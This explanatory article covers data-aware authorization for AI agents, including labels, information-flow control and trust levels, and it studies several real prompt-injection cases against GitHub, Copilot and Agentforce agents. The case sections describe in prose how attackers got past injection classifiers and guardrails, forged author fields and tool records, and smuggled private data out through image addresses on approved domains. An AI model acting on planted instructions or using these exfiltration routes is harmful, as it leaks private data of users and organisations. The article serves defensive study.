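# Trusted and untrusted data, and data that must not be combined, in AI agent authorization

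## What an agent's authorization has to decide about data

An AI agent is a system in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools, which are programs that read files, search the web, query databases or send messages. Before an action happens, software decides whether the agent may take that action on the given data. This decision is called authorization. Most authorization software today checks one action at a time, but an agent can leak data through a sequence of actions that were each permitted. To prevent this, authorization has to take into account where data came from, where it may go, how long it may be kept and what it must not be combined with.

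### Agents, context and tool calls

The definition in NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training* (2026), a joint paper by the US standards institute and two US security agencies, has two parts: at least one generative model, and "scaffolding software" that gives the model tools. ("Super intelligence" here just means AI. An executive order of September 2026 imposed the term on federal agencies, according to Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*.)

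The model only produces text. Some of that text is a structured request, known as a tool call, which contains the name of a tool and the values to pass to it. The scaffolding software recognises the request, runs the tool and adds the result to the model's context. The context is all the text the model receives as input for its next step: the user's request, the developer's standing instructions, and every web page, email and file that earlier tool calls brought in.

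*Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a NIST concept paper (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), describes an agent architecture that takes in instructions, fetches more context based on them, processes the results, possibly acts, and returns a response. Agents repeat this loop many times. Each fetch adds to the context, and anything in the context can influence the next tool call. Many agents connect to tools and data sources through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard.

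### What ordinary authorization checks

Ordinary authorization is based on an identity (who is asking), a resource (the file, mailbox or database) and an action (read, write, delete, send). An administrator writes rules that connect them, such as "payroll clerks may read the payroll file", and a program checks each request against the rules.

Agents are usually authorized through OAuth, a standard that MCP has adopted as its primary authorization method. When someone connects an agent to a mail account, they see a consent screen. If they agree, an authorization server issues a token, a piece of data that the agent's software sends with every request. The token has one or more scopes, which are short strings such as `mail.send` or `payroll.read` that each stand for a range of actions on a service. The mail service checks that the token is genuine, that it is still valid, and that its scopes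 cover the request, then sends the mail.

Scopes are coarse, which is a familiar complaint among people who work on identity systems. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a blog post from August 2026, traces an OAuth extension called Rich Authorization Requests to this complaint. The extension lets a program request something as narrow as one payment of a specific sum to one payee. Similarly, a permission to send mail only to named colleagues would stop many leaks. But even the narrowest such permission describes a request in isolation, and an ordinary token doesn't record what the agent read before making it.

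### Three permitted steps and one leak

Suppose a firm's accounts department runs an agent that is allowed to read public web pages, read the payroll file and send email. The payroll clerk asks it to compare the firm's salaries with a survey on a public website and email a summary to the finance director.

Someone has added an instruction to the survey page for any payroll assistant to send the complete file to a certain address "for verification". The agent reads the page and the file, then sends two emails, one of which delivers the file to the stranger. The log shows no violation, because the agent is allowed to read a public page, read the payroll file on the clerk's behalf, and send email.

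The file can also leak with no stranger involved and nothing malicious on the survey page. The agent might look up the finance director in the address book, pick someone with the same surname at an outside recruitment firm, and attach the whole file because a summary seemed to lack detail. It would make the same three kinds of tool calls as before, and they would pass the same checks.

The two leaks have the same outcome but are separate problems. An attacker chooses the words on the page, watches what happens and tries again with different words, while nobody is directing a mistake. Keeping the stranger's text away from the agent may stop the first leak and do nothing about the second. NIST, NSA and CISA make a similar distinction for AI systems that escape their operators' controls. They use the term "control incident" only for significant "uninstructed" actions, meaning those that neither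 the operator nor an adversary directed. National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script* explains that an action produced by planted text therefore counts as instructed. The agencies wrote their definition with training and evaluation in mind, and a misaddressed email would often be too minor to meet it, but the same distinction applies here.

Filtering data by the user's own permissions and asking a person to approve each step both offer limited protection here. *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* (Help Net Security, 2026) summarises guidance from Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, who advise companies to apply the filter before any data enters the context. This helps prevent an agent from showing people records they could not otherwise open, but it lets the payroll file through when the user is the payroll clerk,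 who can already open it. NIST warns that agents that request approval too often train people to click "allow" by reflex, much as attackers wear people down with repeated login notifications, and approvals given by reflex protect very little.

Rittenhouse and Johnson also want a policy engine to evaluate each tool call. A policy engine is ordinary program code, outside the model, that allows a tool call, blocks it or refers it to a person. It is the natural place to check for the payroll leak, but it can catch the leak only if it has information about the data as well as the request.

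### Prompt injection

The line on the survey page is a prompt injection, which is text placed in content the agent reads to make it act for the attacker. The software developer Simon Willison coined the term, naming it after SQL injection, an older attack on databases. In SQL injection, a program builds a database command by joining its own code to whatever a visitor typed, so if the visitor typed code, the database runs it. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so that the database never treats the text as code.

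Language models have no barrier between instructions and data like the one in a database. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, attributes this to the model receiving the user's request, the developer's instructions and the fetched web page as one sequence of tokens, the small pieces of text that it processes. Developers can mark where each part came from and train the model to give some parts more weight than others, but this only produces a learned tendency, though it may be a strong one. People also want models to follow instructions in text. For example, an agent that reads a website's directions for filling in a form has to act on them.

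Willison argues from the mechanism and a list of cases, without measurements. In June 2025 he thought there was a "very good chance" that a model would obey a plain malicious sentence on a web page. That is not a success rate for the models of late 2026, which may resist crude attempts far better. He names seventeen products or features in which researchers had reported this kind of data theft since April 2023. He says vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the route by which the data left, so most of the fixes did not involve getting the model to tell instructions from data.

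He is also scornful of filters that claim to catch 95% of attacks. If each attempt had an independent 5% chance of getting through, an attacker would have a better than even chance of succeeding at least once in 14 attempts. Real attempts aren't independent, and an attacker who learns from failures should do better than that. A filter that caught 95% of the agent's own mistakes would be more useful, because nobody is searching for the 5% it misses.

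Willison calls the conditions for a successful theft the lethal trifecta: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally, all in one agent. From here on, untrusted data means data that someone without authority over the task could have written or altered. External communication includes much more than email. For example, stolen text can leave inside the web address of an image that a tool fetches or a link that the user clicks. The payroll agent has all three properties, and removing any one stops the stranger's attack. Without the untrusted page there are no planted instructions, without the payroll file there is nothing to steal, and without external communication the file cannot leave. Willison defined the trifecta as a warning about attackers. The recruitment-firm mistake needs only private data and external communication, so an agent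 that avoids the trifecta can still send the payroll to the wrong person.

### Four kinds of rule

Rules that take data into account come in four main kinds, and most real systems use more than one.

- Rules on trust in sources limit what an agent may do after it has read data that an outsider could have written. The payroll agent, having read the survey page, might lose the right to send anything until the clerk has looked at the draft.
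- Rules on permitted destinations limit where data can go. A destination is any person, address, channel or store to which the agent can send data, so a shared folder counts as much as a mailbox does. If payroll data may go only to the finance director and the head of personnel, both leaks fail.
- Retention rules cover what an agent may store, for how long and for what later use. Suppose the agent saves the salary figures in its notes, and a month later a colleague asks it to draft a job advertisement. Nobody has sent anything improper so far, but the figures are now in the context of a task that has no business with them.
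- Combination rules forbid the joining of two sets of data even when the agent may use each of them alone. The firm might let the agent work with payroll and with sickness records, and still forbid a table of what each sick employee earns.

A rule against combining data can matter even when every source is trustworthy and no data leaves the organization, so it is easy to overlook if you think of leaks as theft.

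### Labels and the joining rule

To enforce such rules, a policy engine needs information that the data itself doesn't show. Systems usually record this information in labels, a technique much older than language models.

David Bell and Leonard LaPadula developed the best-known model of confidentiality at the MITRE Corporation in the early 1970s, for the US Air Force. Every document and every user has a level, such as secret or unclassified. Users may not read documents above their own level, and a program that has read secret material may not write to anything less secret. Bell and LaPadula included the second rule because they worried that a program with legitimate access could copy what it reads to a place where others can see it, which is almost exactly the payroll agent's situation.

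In the 1970s Kenneth Biba, also at MITRE, reversed the model's rules to protect integrity, which means keeping unreliable data from corrupting reliable data. In his strict version a trusted program may not read untrusted data, so an agent under that rule could never open a web page. Biba also described a milder policy that suits agents much better. Under it, a program may read any data, but its trust level drops to that of the least trustworthy data it has read.

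Dorothy Denning's 1976 paper *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* gives the general theory. Her model has a set of security classes, a relation that defines whether information may flow from one class to another, and an operator that combines the classes of two inputs into the class of anything computed from both. Under mild assumptions these form a lattice, in which any two classes have a single least restrictive class that is at least as restrictive as both. Software can therefore compute the class of a result automatically, however many inputs went into it.

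Agent designs commonly use a simple form of the two labels. An integrity label marks whether data comes only from trusted sources. A confidentiality label marks who may read it, often as a list of permitted readers. When the agent derives something from several inputs, the joining rule is:

```
integrity(result) = trusted if every input is trusted, otherwise untrusted
readers(result)   = readers(input 1) ∩ readers(input 2) ∩ ... ∩ readers(input n)
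```

The sign ∩ stands for the intersection, the people who appear on every list. A person who reads the result may learn something about any of the inputs, so that person needs permission for all of them. Before a message goes out, the policy engine checks that every recipient is allowed to read its contents. In this procedure, called information-flow control, software labels data, carries the labels over to whatever the agent derives from it, and checks them before each action.

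This version of the payroll task adds two labels to the agent's context. The clerk's request is trusted and open to anyone, so it changes neither label.

| Tool call | Ordinary check | Integrity of the context | Permitted readers of the context |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the survey page | Pass | Untrusted | Anyone |
| Read the payroll file | Pass | Untrusted | Clerk, finance director, head of personnel |
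| Email the stranger or the recruiter | Pass | Untrusted | Neither is on the list, so the engine blocks the email |
| Email the finance director | Pass | Untrusted | On the list, so the confidentiality check passes |

The confidentiality label stops both the attack and the mistake, because the check compares recipients with permitted readers, whatever the reason for the email. In the last row, the finance director may see the payroll, but the survey page could have influenced the email's contents, so a cautious firm might want a person to review it before anyone uses it to set salaries. The integrity label gives the engine a reason to ask for that review. It records who could have written the data, not whether the data is true.

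Under this rule, labels can only get stricter. An agent that reads widely ends up with an untrusted context that hardly anyone may read, and the engine then blocks most useful work. Even the firm's average salary, which the director may be happy to publish, inherits the short reader list of the file it was calculated from. Every workable system therefore needs deliberate exceptions. Declassification releases data to readers its label did not include, as when the director approves the average for the staff newsletter. Endorsement treats some untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose, as when the clerk checks the survey's figures against the printed edition. The person or program that grants an exception can be wrong, and attackers will target these decisions.

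The joining rule also doesn't account for how sensitive the combined data is. Suppose the head of personnel and the company doctor may read the sickness records, but of the two, only the head of personnel may read the payroll file. The rule intersects the reader lists, so she may read the joined table. Reader lists can't determine whether that table is more sensitive than either file alone, which is a question about aggregation, the joining of data items into a whole.

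### NIST's two open questions

In its plans for agent authorization, NIST has raised both the origin of data and the sensitivity of joined data. Booth and colleagues wrote the concept paper for NIST's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE), which builds example systems with commercial products. The paper was open for comment from 5 February to 2 April 2026. Most of it concerns identity, including how to tell an agent from a person, delegate a user's rights to an agent, and log what the agent did. The last of its five areas of interest is tracking data flows. The proposed project would "track and maintain provenance of user prompts and data input sources" so that policy decisions about an agent's actions can draw on it. Provenance is the record of where data came from, and an integrity label is a compressed form of that record.

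The other passage asks reviewers about an agent that gains access to new tools and resources: "how do we determine sensitivity levels of data when ...", and may the user see the aggregated response? The joining rule offers an answer to the second half, provided that someone has labelled the inputs correctly, but not to the first. The standards on the paper's list don't obviously answer the first half either, since they mostly deal with who is asking and with what authority. Next Generation Access Control, an access-control standard, looks like the nearest fit because it can change its policies in response to events, and a read could count as an event.

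*Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), the notice for a November talk by one of the paper's writers, reports more than 600 formal responses. NIST's publications since then have dealt mainly with identity. The August blog post covers shared passwords, long-lived tokens, broad scopes, agents that run under their users' local accounts, and approval fatigue, but not provenance or aggregation. In September, the NCCoE outlined a demonstration of agent identity and authorization in software development and operations, according to FedScoop's *The zero-trust controls federal agencies need for autonomous AI*. That month, NIST (2026) also finalized guidelines on protecting access tokens from misuse, a subject the concept paper had marked as relevant.

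*Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth 2026), a blog post of 27 October by Booth and three co-authors, is the most substantial follow-up. By Biometric Update's account, its ten tenets call for agents with their own identities, access that is minimal, temporary and revocable, and a record of actions that the agent cannot alter. They also separate what an agent may do from what it decides to try, which is the reason for having a policy engine outside the model. The account mentions untrusted input as a way to trick an agent into widening its own access, but does not mention data labels or aggregation. It also reports that NIST admits current standards and technology don't fully meet every tenet.

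The project is at an early stage. NCCoE's project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, offers a summary of the comments on a new resource hub and invites further feedback on a rolling basis. A draft project description is still to come, and the practice guide meant to show working examples will follow the demonstrations.

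## The GitHub issue that led an agent to publish private repository data

In May 2025 the security company Invariant Labs used demonstration repositories on GitHub to carry out a leak much like the payroll one. GitHub hosts software projects in repositories, which hold a project's files and their history. Anyone can read a public repository, but only people the owner chooses can read a private one. Users post issues to report bugs and make requests. They propose a change to the files by opening a pull request, which shows the change to everyone who can read the repository.

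GitHub publishes an MCP server, a program that gives agents tools for reading and writing on GitHub. According to heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server*, the server works on the user's account, so an agent connected through it can reach the same private repositories as its user. The attack did not rely on a bug in the server.

### How each step passed its check

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates the attack on an account that owned several private repositories and a public one containing a simple Pacman game. The account's owner used Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, with the GitHub MCP server connected. The researchers posted an issue containing a prompt injection on the Pacman repository. When the owner asked the agent to look at the open issues there, it followed the injected instructions and published data from the private repositories.

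| Step | Permission check | Why it passed |
|---|---|---|
| A stranger posts an issue on the public repository | May this user post issues here? | The repository accepts issues from everyone on GitHub |
| The agent reads the issues | May the owner's account read this repository? | It is public, and the owner's own |
| The agent reads the private repositories | May the owner's account read these repositories? | They belong to the owner |
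| The agent opens a pull request on the public repository, with private details in it | May the owner's account write here? | The owner controls the repository |
| The stranger reads the pull request | May this user read the repository? | Anyone may |

The pull request disclosed the names of private repositories, the owner's salary, and their plan to move to South America. Each check compared a single request with someone's access rights. None took into account that a stranger's issue had led the agent to read the private repositories, or that the pull request contained data from them.

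The user could still have intervened, because Claude Desktop asks for confirmation of each tool call by default. A request to open private repositories should look odd to someone who only asked about a public one. But Invariant Labs says many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching what the agent does.

Ordinary authorization could also have stopped this attack. If the owner had connected the agent with a token limited to the Pacman repository, the agent could not have read the others. Invariant Labs recommends such limits but finds them rigid. Someone who wants help with all their projects will probably grant access to all of them. Willison's *GitHub MCP Exploited* describes the case as an example of the lethal trifecta.

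Coding agents can publish private material on public GitHub pages without a stranger's involvement. Markovic (2026), in *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*, reports that agents posted internal images, including billing records, from more than 300 organizations. These leaks look like the agents' own mistakes on a large scale, and defences against planted text would do little to prevent them.

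### The same leak in an automated workflow

A similar attack worked a year later on a newer product. In February 2026 GitHub released Agentic Workflows, which let developers describe a job in plain language and have an agent, running on GitHub Copilot or Claude, do it whenever a chosen event occurs. Levi's *GitLost*, published that July, describes how researchers at Noma Security used a public issue to get private data out of such a workflow.

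InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) describes a workflow that started when an issue was assigned. The workflow read the issue's title and body and posted a comment. It could also read the organization's other repositories, including private ones. Noma's issue resembled a request from a vice president of sales after a customer meeting. GitHub's automation assigned it, and the agent fetched the README files from public repositories and a private one, then published them in a comment.

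The researchers tried several wordings to get around GitHub's guardrails. *GitLost Flaw Lets Attackers Trick GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking Private Repos* reports that adding one connecting word made the agent comply with a request it had refused. Levi attributed the problem to a mismatch between where the agent's permissions are held and where its inputs come from.

Levi calls this a critical vulnerability, while Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) blames the configuration. Both views seem fair. A workflow that answers public issues rarely needs to read private repositories, but GitHub's software allowed the combination.

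### One repository per session

Invariant Labs proposed a rule that an agent may use only one repository per session. A policy engine enforces the rule by blocking any repository tool call that names a different repository or owner from an earlier call in the session. In the Pacman case, the rule would have blocked the agent's first request for a private repository.

This is a combination rule, and it works without detecting the attack. It would also stop an agent that copied private details into a public repository by mistake. But it blocks legitimate work that spans repositories, such as changing a library and then updating the program that uses it.

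The rule covers only what passes through the repository tools. An agent that read a private repository and then sent its contents by email would not break the rule, because it used only one repository. Nor would an agent that uploaded a screenshot from its user's computer to a public repository. If the agent keeps notes between sessions, private text can reach a public repository in a later session. Invariant Labs was promoting a product that enforces the rule, though the rule is simple enough for anyone to implement.

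### Hiding what strangers write

Invariant Labs argued that GitHub could not fix the problem by patching its server, because the flaw was in how the parts of the whole agent system worked together. This slightly overstated the case. In December 2025, GitHub (2025) announced lockdown mode, a server option that would have kept the stranger's issue away from the agent.

According to GitHub's documentation, the server in lockdown mode returns issues, pull requests, comments and discussions from a public repository only if their author has push access, which is permission to change the repository's files. Classmethod's *Reducing Prompt Injection Risk with GitHub MCP Lockdown Mode* (2026), a hands-on check from August, describes the same rule. Lockdown mode's protection depends on the server identifying each author's permissions correctly. According to an advisory from the security company Aikido,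 versions up to 1.0.2 could get them wrong and let a malicious user's text through, and version 1.0.3 fixed the fault.

The larger drawback of lockdown is that it hides issues written by strangers, and people open public issue trackers so that strangers can write in them. According to GitHub's documentation, it is acceptable to turn lockdown off for workflows that sort issues, plan work from them or detect spam. The Pacman owner's request was similar. Under lockdown, the agent would have reported only on issues from people who could already change the game's code.

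Agentic Workflows has a more finely graded version called integrity filtering. A gateway between the agent and GitHub gives every item a trust level and removes those below a set minimum before the model receives them. GitHub's documentation defines four levels that a developer can choose as the minimum:

- `merged`: merged pull requests, and changes that are already part of the repository's main branch, whoever wrote them.
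- `approved`: items by the repository's owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories.
- `unapproved`: items by people who have contributed before, and some first-time contributors.
- `none`: everything else, including posts by people with no connection to the project.

Each setting also admits the levels above it. The minimum is `approved` by default in public repositories, while private and internal ones have no automatic filter. Under the public default, a stranger's issue should not reach the agent through the gateway. The workflow that Noma attacked may have had a lower minimum, predated the default, or taken the issue's text directly from the event that started it.

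Maintainers, the people who run a project, can make exceptions by attaching a label that raises a stranger's issue to `approved`. This is endorsement in the sense used for integrity labels, and another label can withdraw it. If a developer switches on an option, a maintainer's thumbs-up also endorses the issue. That is convenient, but people also use a thumbs-up to say thank you, so a maintainer may thank someone for a bug report without thinking about which agents will now read it.

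All these filters address attackers. They do nothing about an agent that misplaces private data after reading only approved text.

### Checks on what the agent publishes

GitHub also checks outgoing data. In August 2025, GitHub (2025) announced that its hosted MCP server would scan the contents of tool calls to public repositories and block any that contained exposed secrets, which its documentation describes as tokens, keys and other credentials. This helps with both attacks and mistakes, because a credential looks the same whoever caused the agent to include it. The scan would not have stopped the Pacman leak, because details such as a salary or a plan to move abroad are ordinary prose.

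GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes further protections in Agentic Workflows. The system keeps secrets away from the agent, restricts its network connections with a firewall, and vets its writes before they take effect. The vetting limits the kinds and number of writes, removes secrets and moderates content. These measures considerably reduce the possible damage. But a workflow whose job is to post comments has permission to post them, and the vetting may not catch a comment that contains a private README, because the text looks much like that of a public one.

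To catch the leak, the software would have to record that the text came from a private repository. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, a post from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, says that the system already labels private data and tracks where it flows, but does not yet act on the labels. Integrity filtering therefore "cannot prevent leaks across repos". For now, a developer who wants to rule out such leaks has to limit which repositories the workflow can reach. By default, the setting allows every repository that the workflow's token can access.

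### Public text can be trustworthy and private text hostile

Data can be public and trusted, or private and untrusted. GitHub's defaults, however, come close to treating all public data as untrusted and all private data as trusted, since they filter public repositories but not private ones.

Much public text comes from people with authority over the task. Anyone can read a maintainer's comment on a public issue, but a stranger cannot edit it. GitHub gives its highest trust level to changes that maintainers have merged into the main branch, so the main code of a public project ranks above an employee's comment in a private repository. An agent that treated the public code as hostile would be useless for working on it. But the high trust level depends on the maintainers' review, and a reviewer can miss malicious text in a long contribution.

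Outsiders can also get text into private repositories. GitHub's FAQ explains how to have the task tracker Jira start a workflow whenever someone creates a Jira issue, and pass along the issue's summary. If customers can create those issues, their words enter a workflow that may be running in a private repository. An employee who pastes a customer's complaint into a private issue does the same by hand, and GitHub then classifies the complaint as `approved`. GitHub Next acknowledges that the system will also label an attacker's comments as `approved` if the attacker takes over a maintainer's account.

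"Private" is also too coarse a confidentiality label. A company might have one private repository that only its lawyers can read and another that it shares with a contractor. Copying text from the first to the second leaks it to the contractor, even though it never becomes public. GitHub Next's design addresses this by giving each repository its own tag.

Judging trust by author is better than judging it by repository, but the software or the model then has to identify the author correctly.

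### Forging an author's name or a tool's record

Every item that an agent reads from GitHub mixes text from several sources. GitHub fills in the name of a comment's author, and the author writes the body. In an email, the mail service fills in the sender's address, and the sender writes the subject and message. An attacker controls only some of these fields, so a single trust label for the whole item will be wrong about part of it.

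Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, show how attackers can exploit this. The team, from Seoul National University, the University of Illinois Urbana-Champaign and the company Largosoft, separates an agent's instructions *I* from its trusted data *T*, which a tool or the agent's own software generates, and its untrusted data *U*, which an attacker may control. The attacker adds text *A* to the untrusted data. In the familiar kind of prompt injection, the model behaves as if *A* were part of its instructions. In agent data injection, it behaves as if *A* were part of the trusted data:

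```
instruction injection:  LLM(I, (T, U + A)) ≈ LLM(I + A, (T, U))
data injection:         LLM(I, (T, U + A)) ≈ LLM(I, (T + A, U))
```

Here + means one text contains the other, and ≈ means the model's output is almost the same. Under data injection, the agent keeps working on the user's task, but with false information about who wrote something or what has already happened.

The attack relies on delimiters, which are the quotation marks, brackets and line breaks that separate one field from the next. An attacker writes a comment whose body imitates the end of that comment and the start of another, supposedly by a maintainer. SQL injection uses a similar trick, but a database recognises only exact delimiters. In the team's tests, language models often accepted delimiters that a conventional program would treat as ordinary characters, and even some that used the wrong symbols.

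The researchers demonstrated three main attacks on real products:

- A product review imitated a button on a shopping page and reused the number that the agent's software had given the real "Buy Now" button. An agent that set out to read more reviews bought the product instead. This worked on Claude in Chrome, Google's Antigravity and the open-source Nanobrowser. It failed on ChatGPT Atlas, which gives page elements random identifiers that an attacker can't predict.
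- A comment on a GitHub issue imitated a second comment by a maintainer. The user had asked the agent to apply the maintainer's fix, and the agent ran the attacker's command. Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI were all vulnerable.
- The description of a pull request imitated the record of a tool call, as if the agent had already fetched the proposed code and found it harmless. The same three coding agents then approved and merged the real, malicious code without reading it.

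The team also got ChatGPT and Claude to name the wrong sender of an email. In a connected Slack workspace, Claude Code mistook an ordinary member's message for one from the channel's administrator. The message was another example of untrusted text in a private place.

The coding agents asked for confirmation before running a command, but the model wrote the explanation the user saw. In one example, Claude Code described the attacker's package as the maintainer's suggestion. A user who approved it would have been following the right policy but relying on a false description.

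### Success rates and defences

These product attacks are demonstrations, so they don't measure how often an attempt would succeed. To measure success rates, Choi and colleagues ran two separate experiments. In the first, they gave six models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google structured data containing a forged record and asked simple questions, such as who wrote the first comment. The models returned the attacker's information in 31.3% to 43.3% of cases when the data was in JSON, a common text format for records, and in 33.3% to 100% of cases when it was on web pages.

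The models also made mistakes when nobody was attacking. They answered between 81.2% and 84.8% of the JSON questions correctly, so roughly one answer in six was marked wrong, though the scoring compared strings of text and may have rejected some acceptable answers. An agent that misreads an author field can mistake a stranger's advice for a maintainer's even if nobody forged the field.

The second experiment used a complete agent, running GPT-5.2, on simulated office, chat, banking and travel tasks. With no added defence, 49.1% of 108 data injection attacks succeeded, compared with 0.2% of 935 older attacks that planted instructions. The second figure probably understates the model's vulnerability to planted instructions, because the older attacks came from an existing benchmark and were not adapted to the model. But training a model to ignore planted commands evidently doesn't teach it to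 recognise forged records.

Defences aimed at planted instructions did badly. Llama Prompt Guard 2, a classifier that screens incoming text, detected none of the 108 data attacks. AlignmentCheck, which uses a model to judge whether the agent's actions fit the user's request, let 94 through, since the actions did fit the request. It referred the other 14 to a person, but gave the right reason for only one. The most useful defences had very different costs:

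| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None added | 49.1% | 86.5% |
| Random suffixes on field names | 28.7% | 83.3% |
| Progent, which checks tool calls against written policies | 22.2% | 81.4% |
| CaMeL in strict mode, which tracks where each value came from | 0% | 36.5% |

Random suffixes make it hard to forge a particular field, because the attacker doesn't know what the field is called in that run. They help less when the agent processes a whole list. For example, an agent that adds up the transactions in an account may include a fake transaction even though the fake's field names are wrong. CaMeL's strict mode stopped every attack by enforcing rules on data derived from untrusted fields, but the agent completed fewer than half as many ordinary tasks as before.

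The figures are limited to six models from 2025, and the second experiment used only one of them. The attacker has to know how the agent formats its data. This is easy to find out when the formatting happens on the user's computer, but for the forged tool records the researchers had to extract the format from the models. OpenAI, Google and Anthropic acknowledged the reports, so their products may have changed since the tests.

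Setting trust for each field requires ordinary code to read the fields before the model does. GitHub's gateway does this when deciding which items to admit. It takes the author's status from GitHub's own metadata, so a stranger's comment that imitates a maintainer should still get the stranger's trust level. But if the developer lowers the minimum trust level to let strangers' comments in, the model receives the imitation too. An instruction to follow only the maintainer's advice then depends on the model reading the names correctly. A safer agent would use code to pass on only the comments whose real author is a maintainer. But approval labels apply to a whole issue, so a maintainer who approves a useful bug report also approves any forged comment or tool record further down in its text.

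## Approved destinations as a way out: Microsoft 365 Copilot and Salesforce Agentforce

The agents in the GitHub cases leaked private text by posting it where strangers could read it. One remedy is to let an agent send data only to approved destinations. Microsoft and Salesforce were doing this in 2025, at least for the images in their assistants' answers, but researchers got data out through addresses on the approved lists.

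### What counts as a destination

An email recipient is the easiest destination to recognise because the tool call specifies it. The readers of a shared document are harder to predict, since anyone who can open the document can read a paragraph added to it, including people who get access later.

Requesting information also sends information, because the server receives the full web address. If an agent requests a company logo and appends someone's salary to the address, the server returns the logo and keeps the salary in its log. An agent can also leak data this way by mistake. If it types "Hartley takeover price" into a public search engine while working on a secret bid, the search company gets a hint of the bid.

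Links and images in an agent's answer can carry data in the same way, though the client (the browser or app that displays the answer) sends the request rather than the agent. A link sends nothing until the user clicks it. An image is worse because the client usually loads it automatically. A policy engine that only checks tool calls will miss both, since writing them into an answer isn't a tool call.

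### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot is an assistant that answers questions about a user's work. It searches the user's mailbox, files, internal sites and Teams chats, and adds what it finds to the model's context. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, used a single email to get data out of Copilot.

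Anyone could send the email. The researchers got past Microsoft's classifier for blocking prompt injections by writing the instructions as if to the email's recipient, without mentioning AI. To get Copilot to retrieve the email, they made it very long, with sections on many common office topics and the instructions repeated in each. If an employee later asked Copilot about one of these topics, it would probably bring the email into its context. The employee didn't have to open the email or click on anything, which is why the researchers call the attack "zero-click".

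The attacker could reach everything in Copilot's context, though not everything the user could open. The context included the conversation so far, the documents and messages Copilot had retrieved, and details such as the user's name. The attacker didn't need to know what was there, because they could use the email to ask for the most sensitive item.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of the attack, notes that Copilot could not send email on its own, so the attacker had to get the data out through Copilot's answer. Copilot deleted external links from its answers, and a content security policy, a set of restrictions that a website gives the browser, limited images to approved domains. The link filter missed a less common way of writing links, in which the address comes at the end of the text. Writing an image's address the same way got the image past the filter, but the browser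 refused to load it because the attacker's server was not on an approved domain.

The team therefore looked for an approved domain that would pass the request on. SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, could fetch outside content, but only after the user had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service did the same without an invitation. The browser contacted only Microsoft, asking the Teams service for an image. Teams then fetched the attacker's address, and the attacker's server logged the data in that address.

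EchoLeak is listed in the public catalogue of security flaws as CVE-2025-32711. Its severity score is 9.3 out of 10, according to The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction* (2025), which reports no evidence of malicious use. Aim Labs told Microsoft about the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft finished the patch in May, before the disclosure on 11 June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Microsoft made the change on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install.

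Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft now strips the less common links and embedded images from incoming external content, and that its patches added options to stop Copilot from using external messages in some contexts. These changes address how an attack gets in as well as how data gets out, but an assistant that ignores outside email can't tell a salesperson what a customer has asked for in one.

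Ravia thinks the email's most suspicious feature was that it came from outside the organization and referred to internal data. He calls this an "LLM Scope Violation" and argues that software should look for it directly, however the data leaves. His company was selling a product that does this. The idea is attractive but needs refinement, because a customer who asks about a late delivery is also an outsider referring to internal data.

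A year later, researchers at Varonis found a similar weakness in Copilot's enterprise search. Their attack, SearchLeak, required the victim to click a link to a genuine Microsoft address. eSecurity Planet's *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot* lists three flaws in the chain. One let the link carry the attacker's prompt, another was a timing error in how Copilot displayed its answer, and the third let an outsider choose an address for a Bing server to contact, much as the Teams service had allowed. Bing was already on the list of approved image domains that Ravia published in 2025.

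SearchLeak could expose emails, calendar details and indexed files. The Hacker News (2026) identifies it as CVE-2026-42824 and reports severity scores of 6.5 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database, though Microsoft also rated it critical. Microsoft again fixed the flaw on its own servers, and Varonis had shown only a proof of concept. Trust in Microsoft's domain also helped the attacker get in. The Next Web (2026) notes that filters for suspicious links were unlikely to flag one that led to a real Microsoft site.

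### ForcedLeak

Agentforce is Salesforce's platform for agents that work with a company's customer records. Noma Security reported a leak in Agentforce to Salesforce on 28 July 2025. A forum post by Nytro (2025), *ForcedLeak*, reproduces Noma's full report.

The attacker's text entered through Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that puts a contact form on a company's public website and saves each submission in the customer database as a lead, or potential customer. The name and company fields were too short to hold useful instructions, but the description field accepted 42,000 characters. The text stayed in the database until an employee asked the agent to look at the lead and answer the questions in it.

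That request makes the case difficult for any defence that relies on distinguishing instructions from data. The employee had a good reason to want the stranger's questions answered, and some of the planted instructions were phrased as questions. One asked for the email addresses of the company's other leads. A sensible assistant would refuse, but to do so it would have to recognise that the question was improper, not just that it came from a stranger.

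In the demonstration, the agent collected those addresses from the database. Noma says an attacker could also have reached contact details, sales plans and records of past conversations.

As in EchoLeak, the data went out inside the address of an image. Salesforce's registration of `my-salesforce-cms.com` had expired but, as Willison explains, the domain was still on the company's list of approved image domains. Noma bought the domain for $5 and received the data directly, whereas EchoLeak needed a service to relay it.

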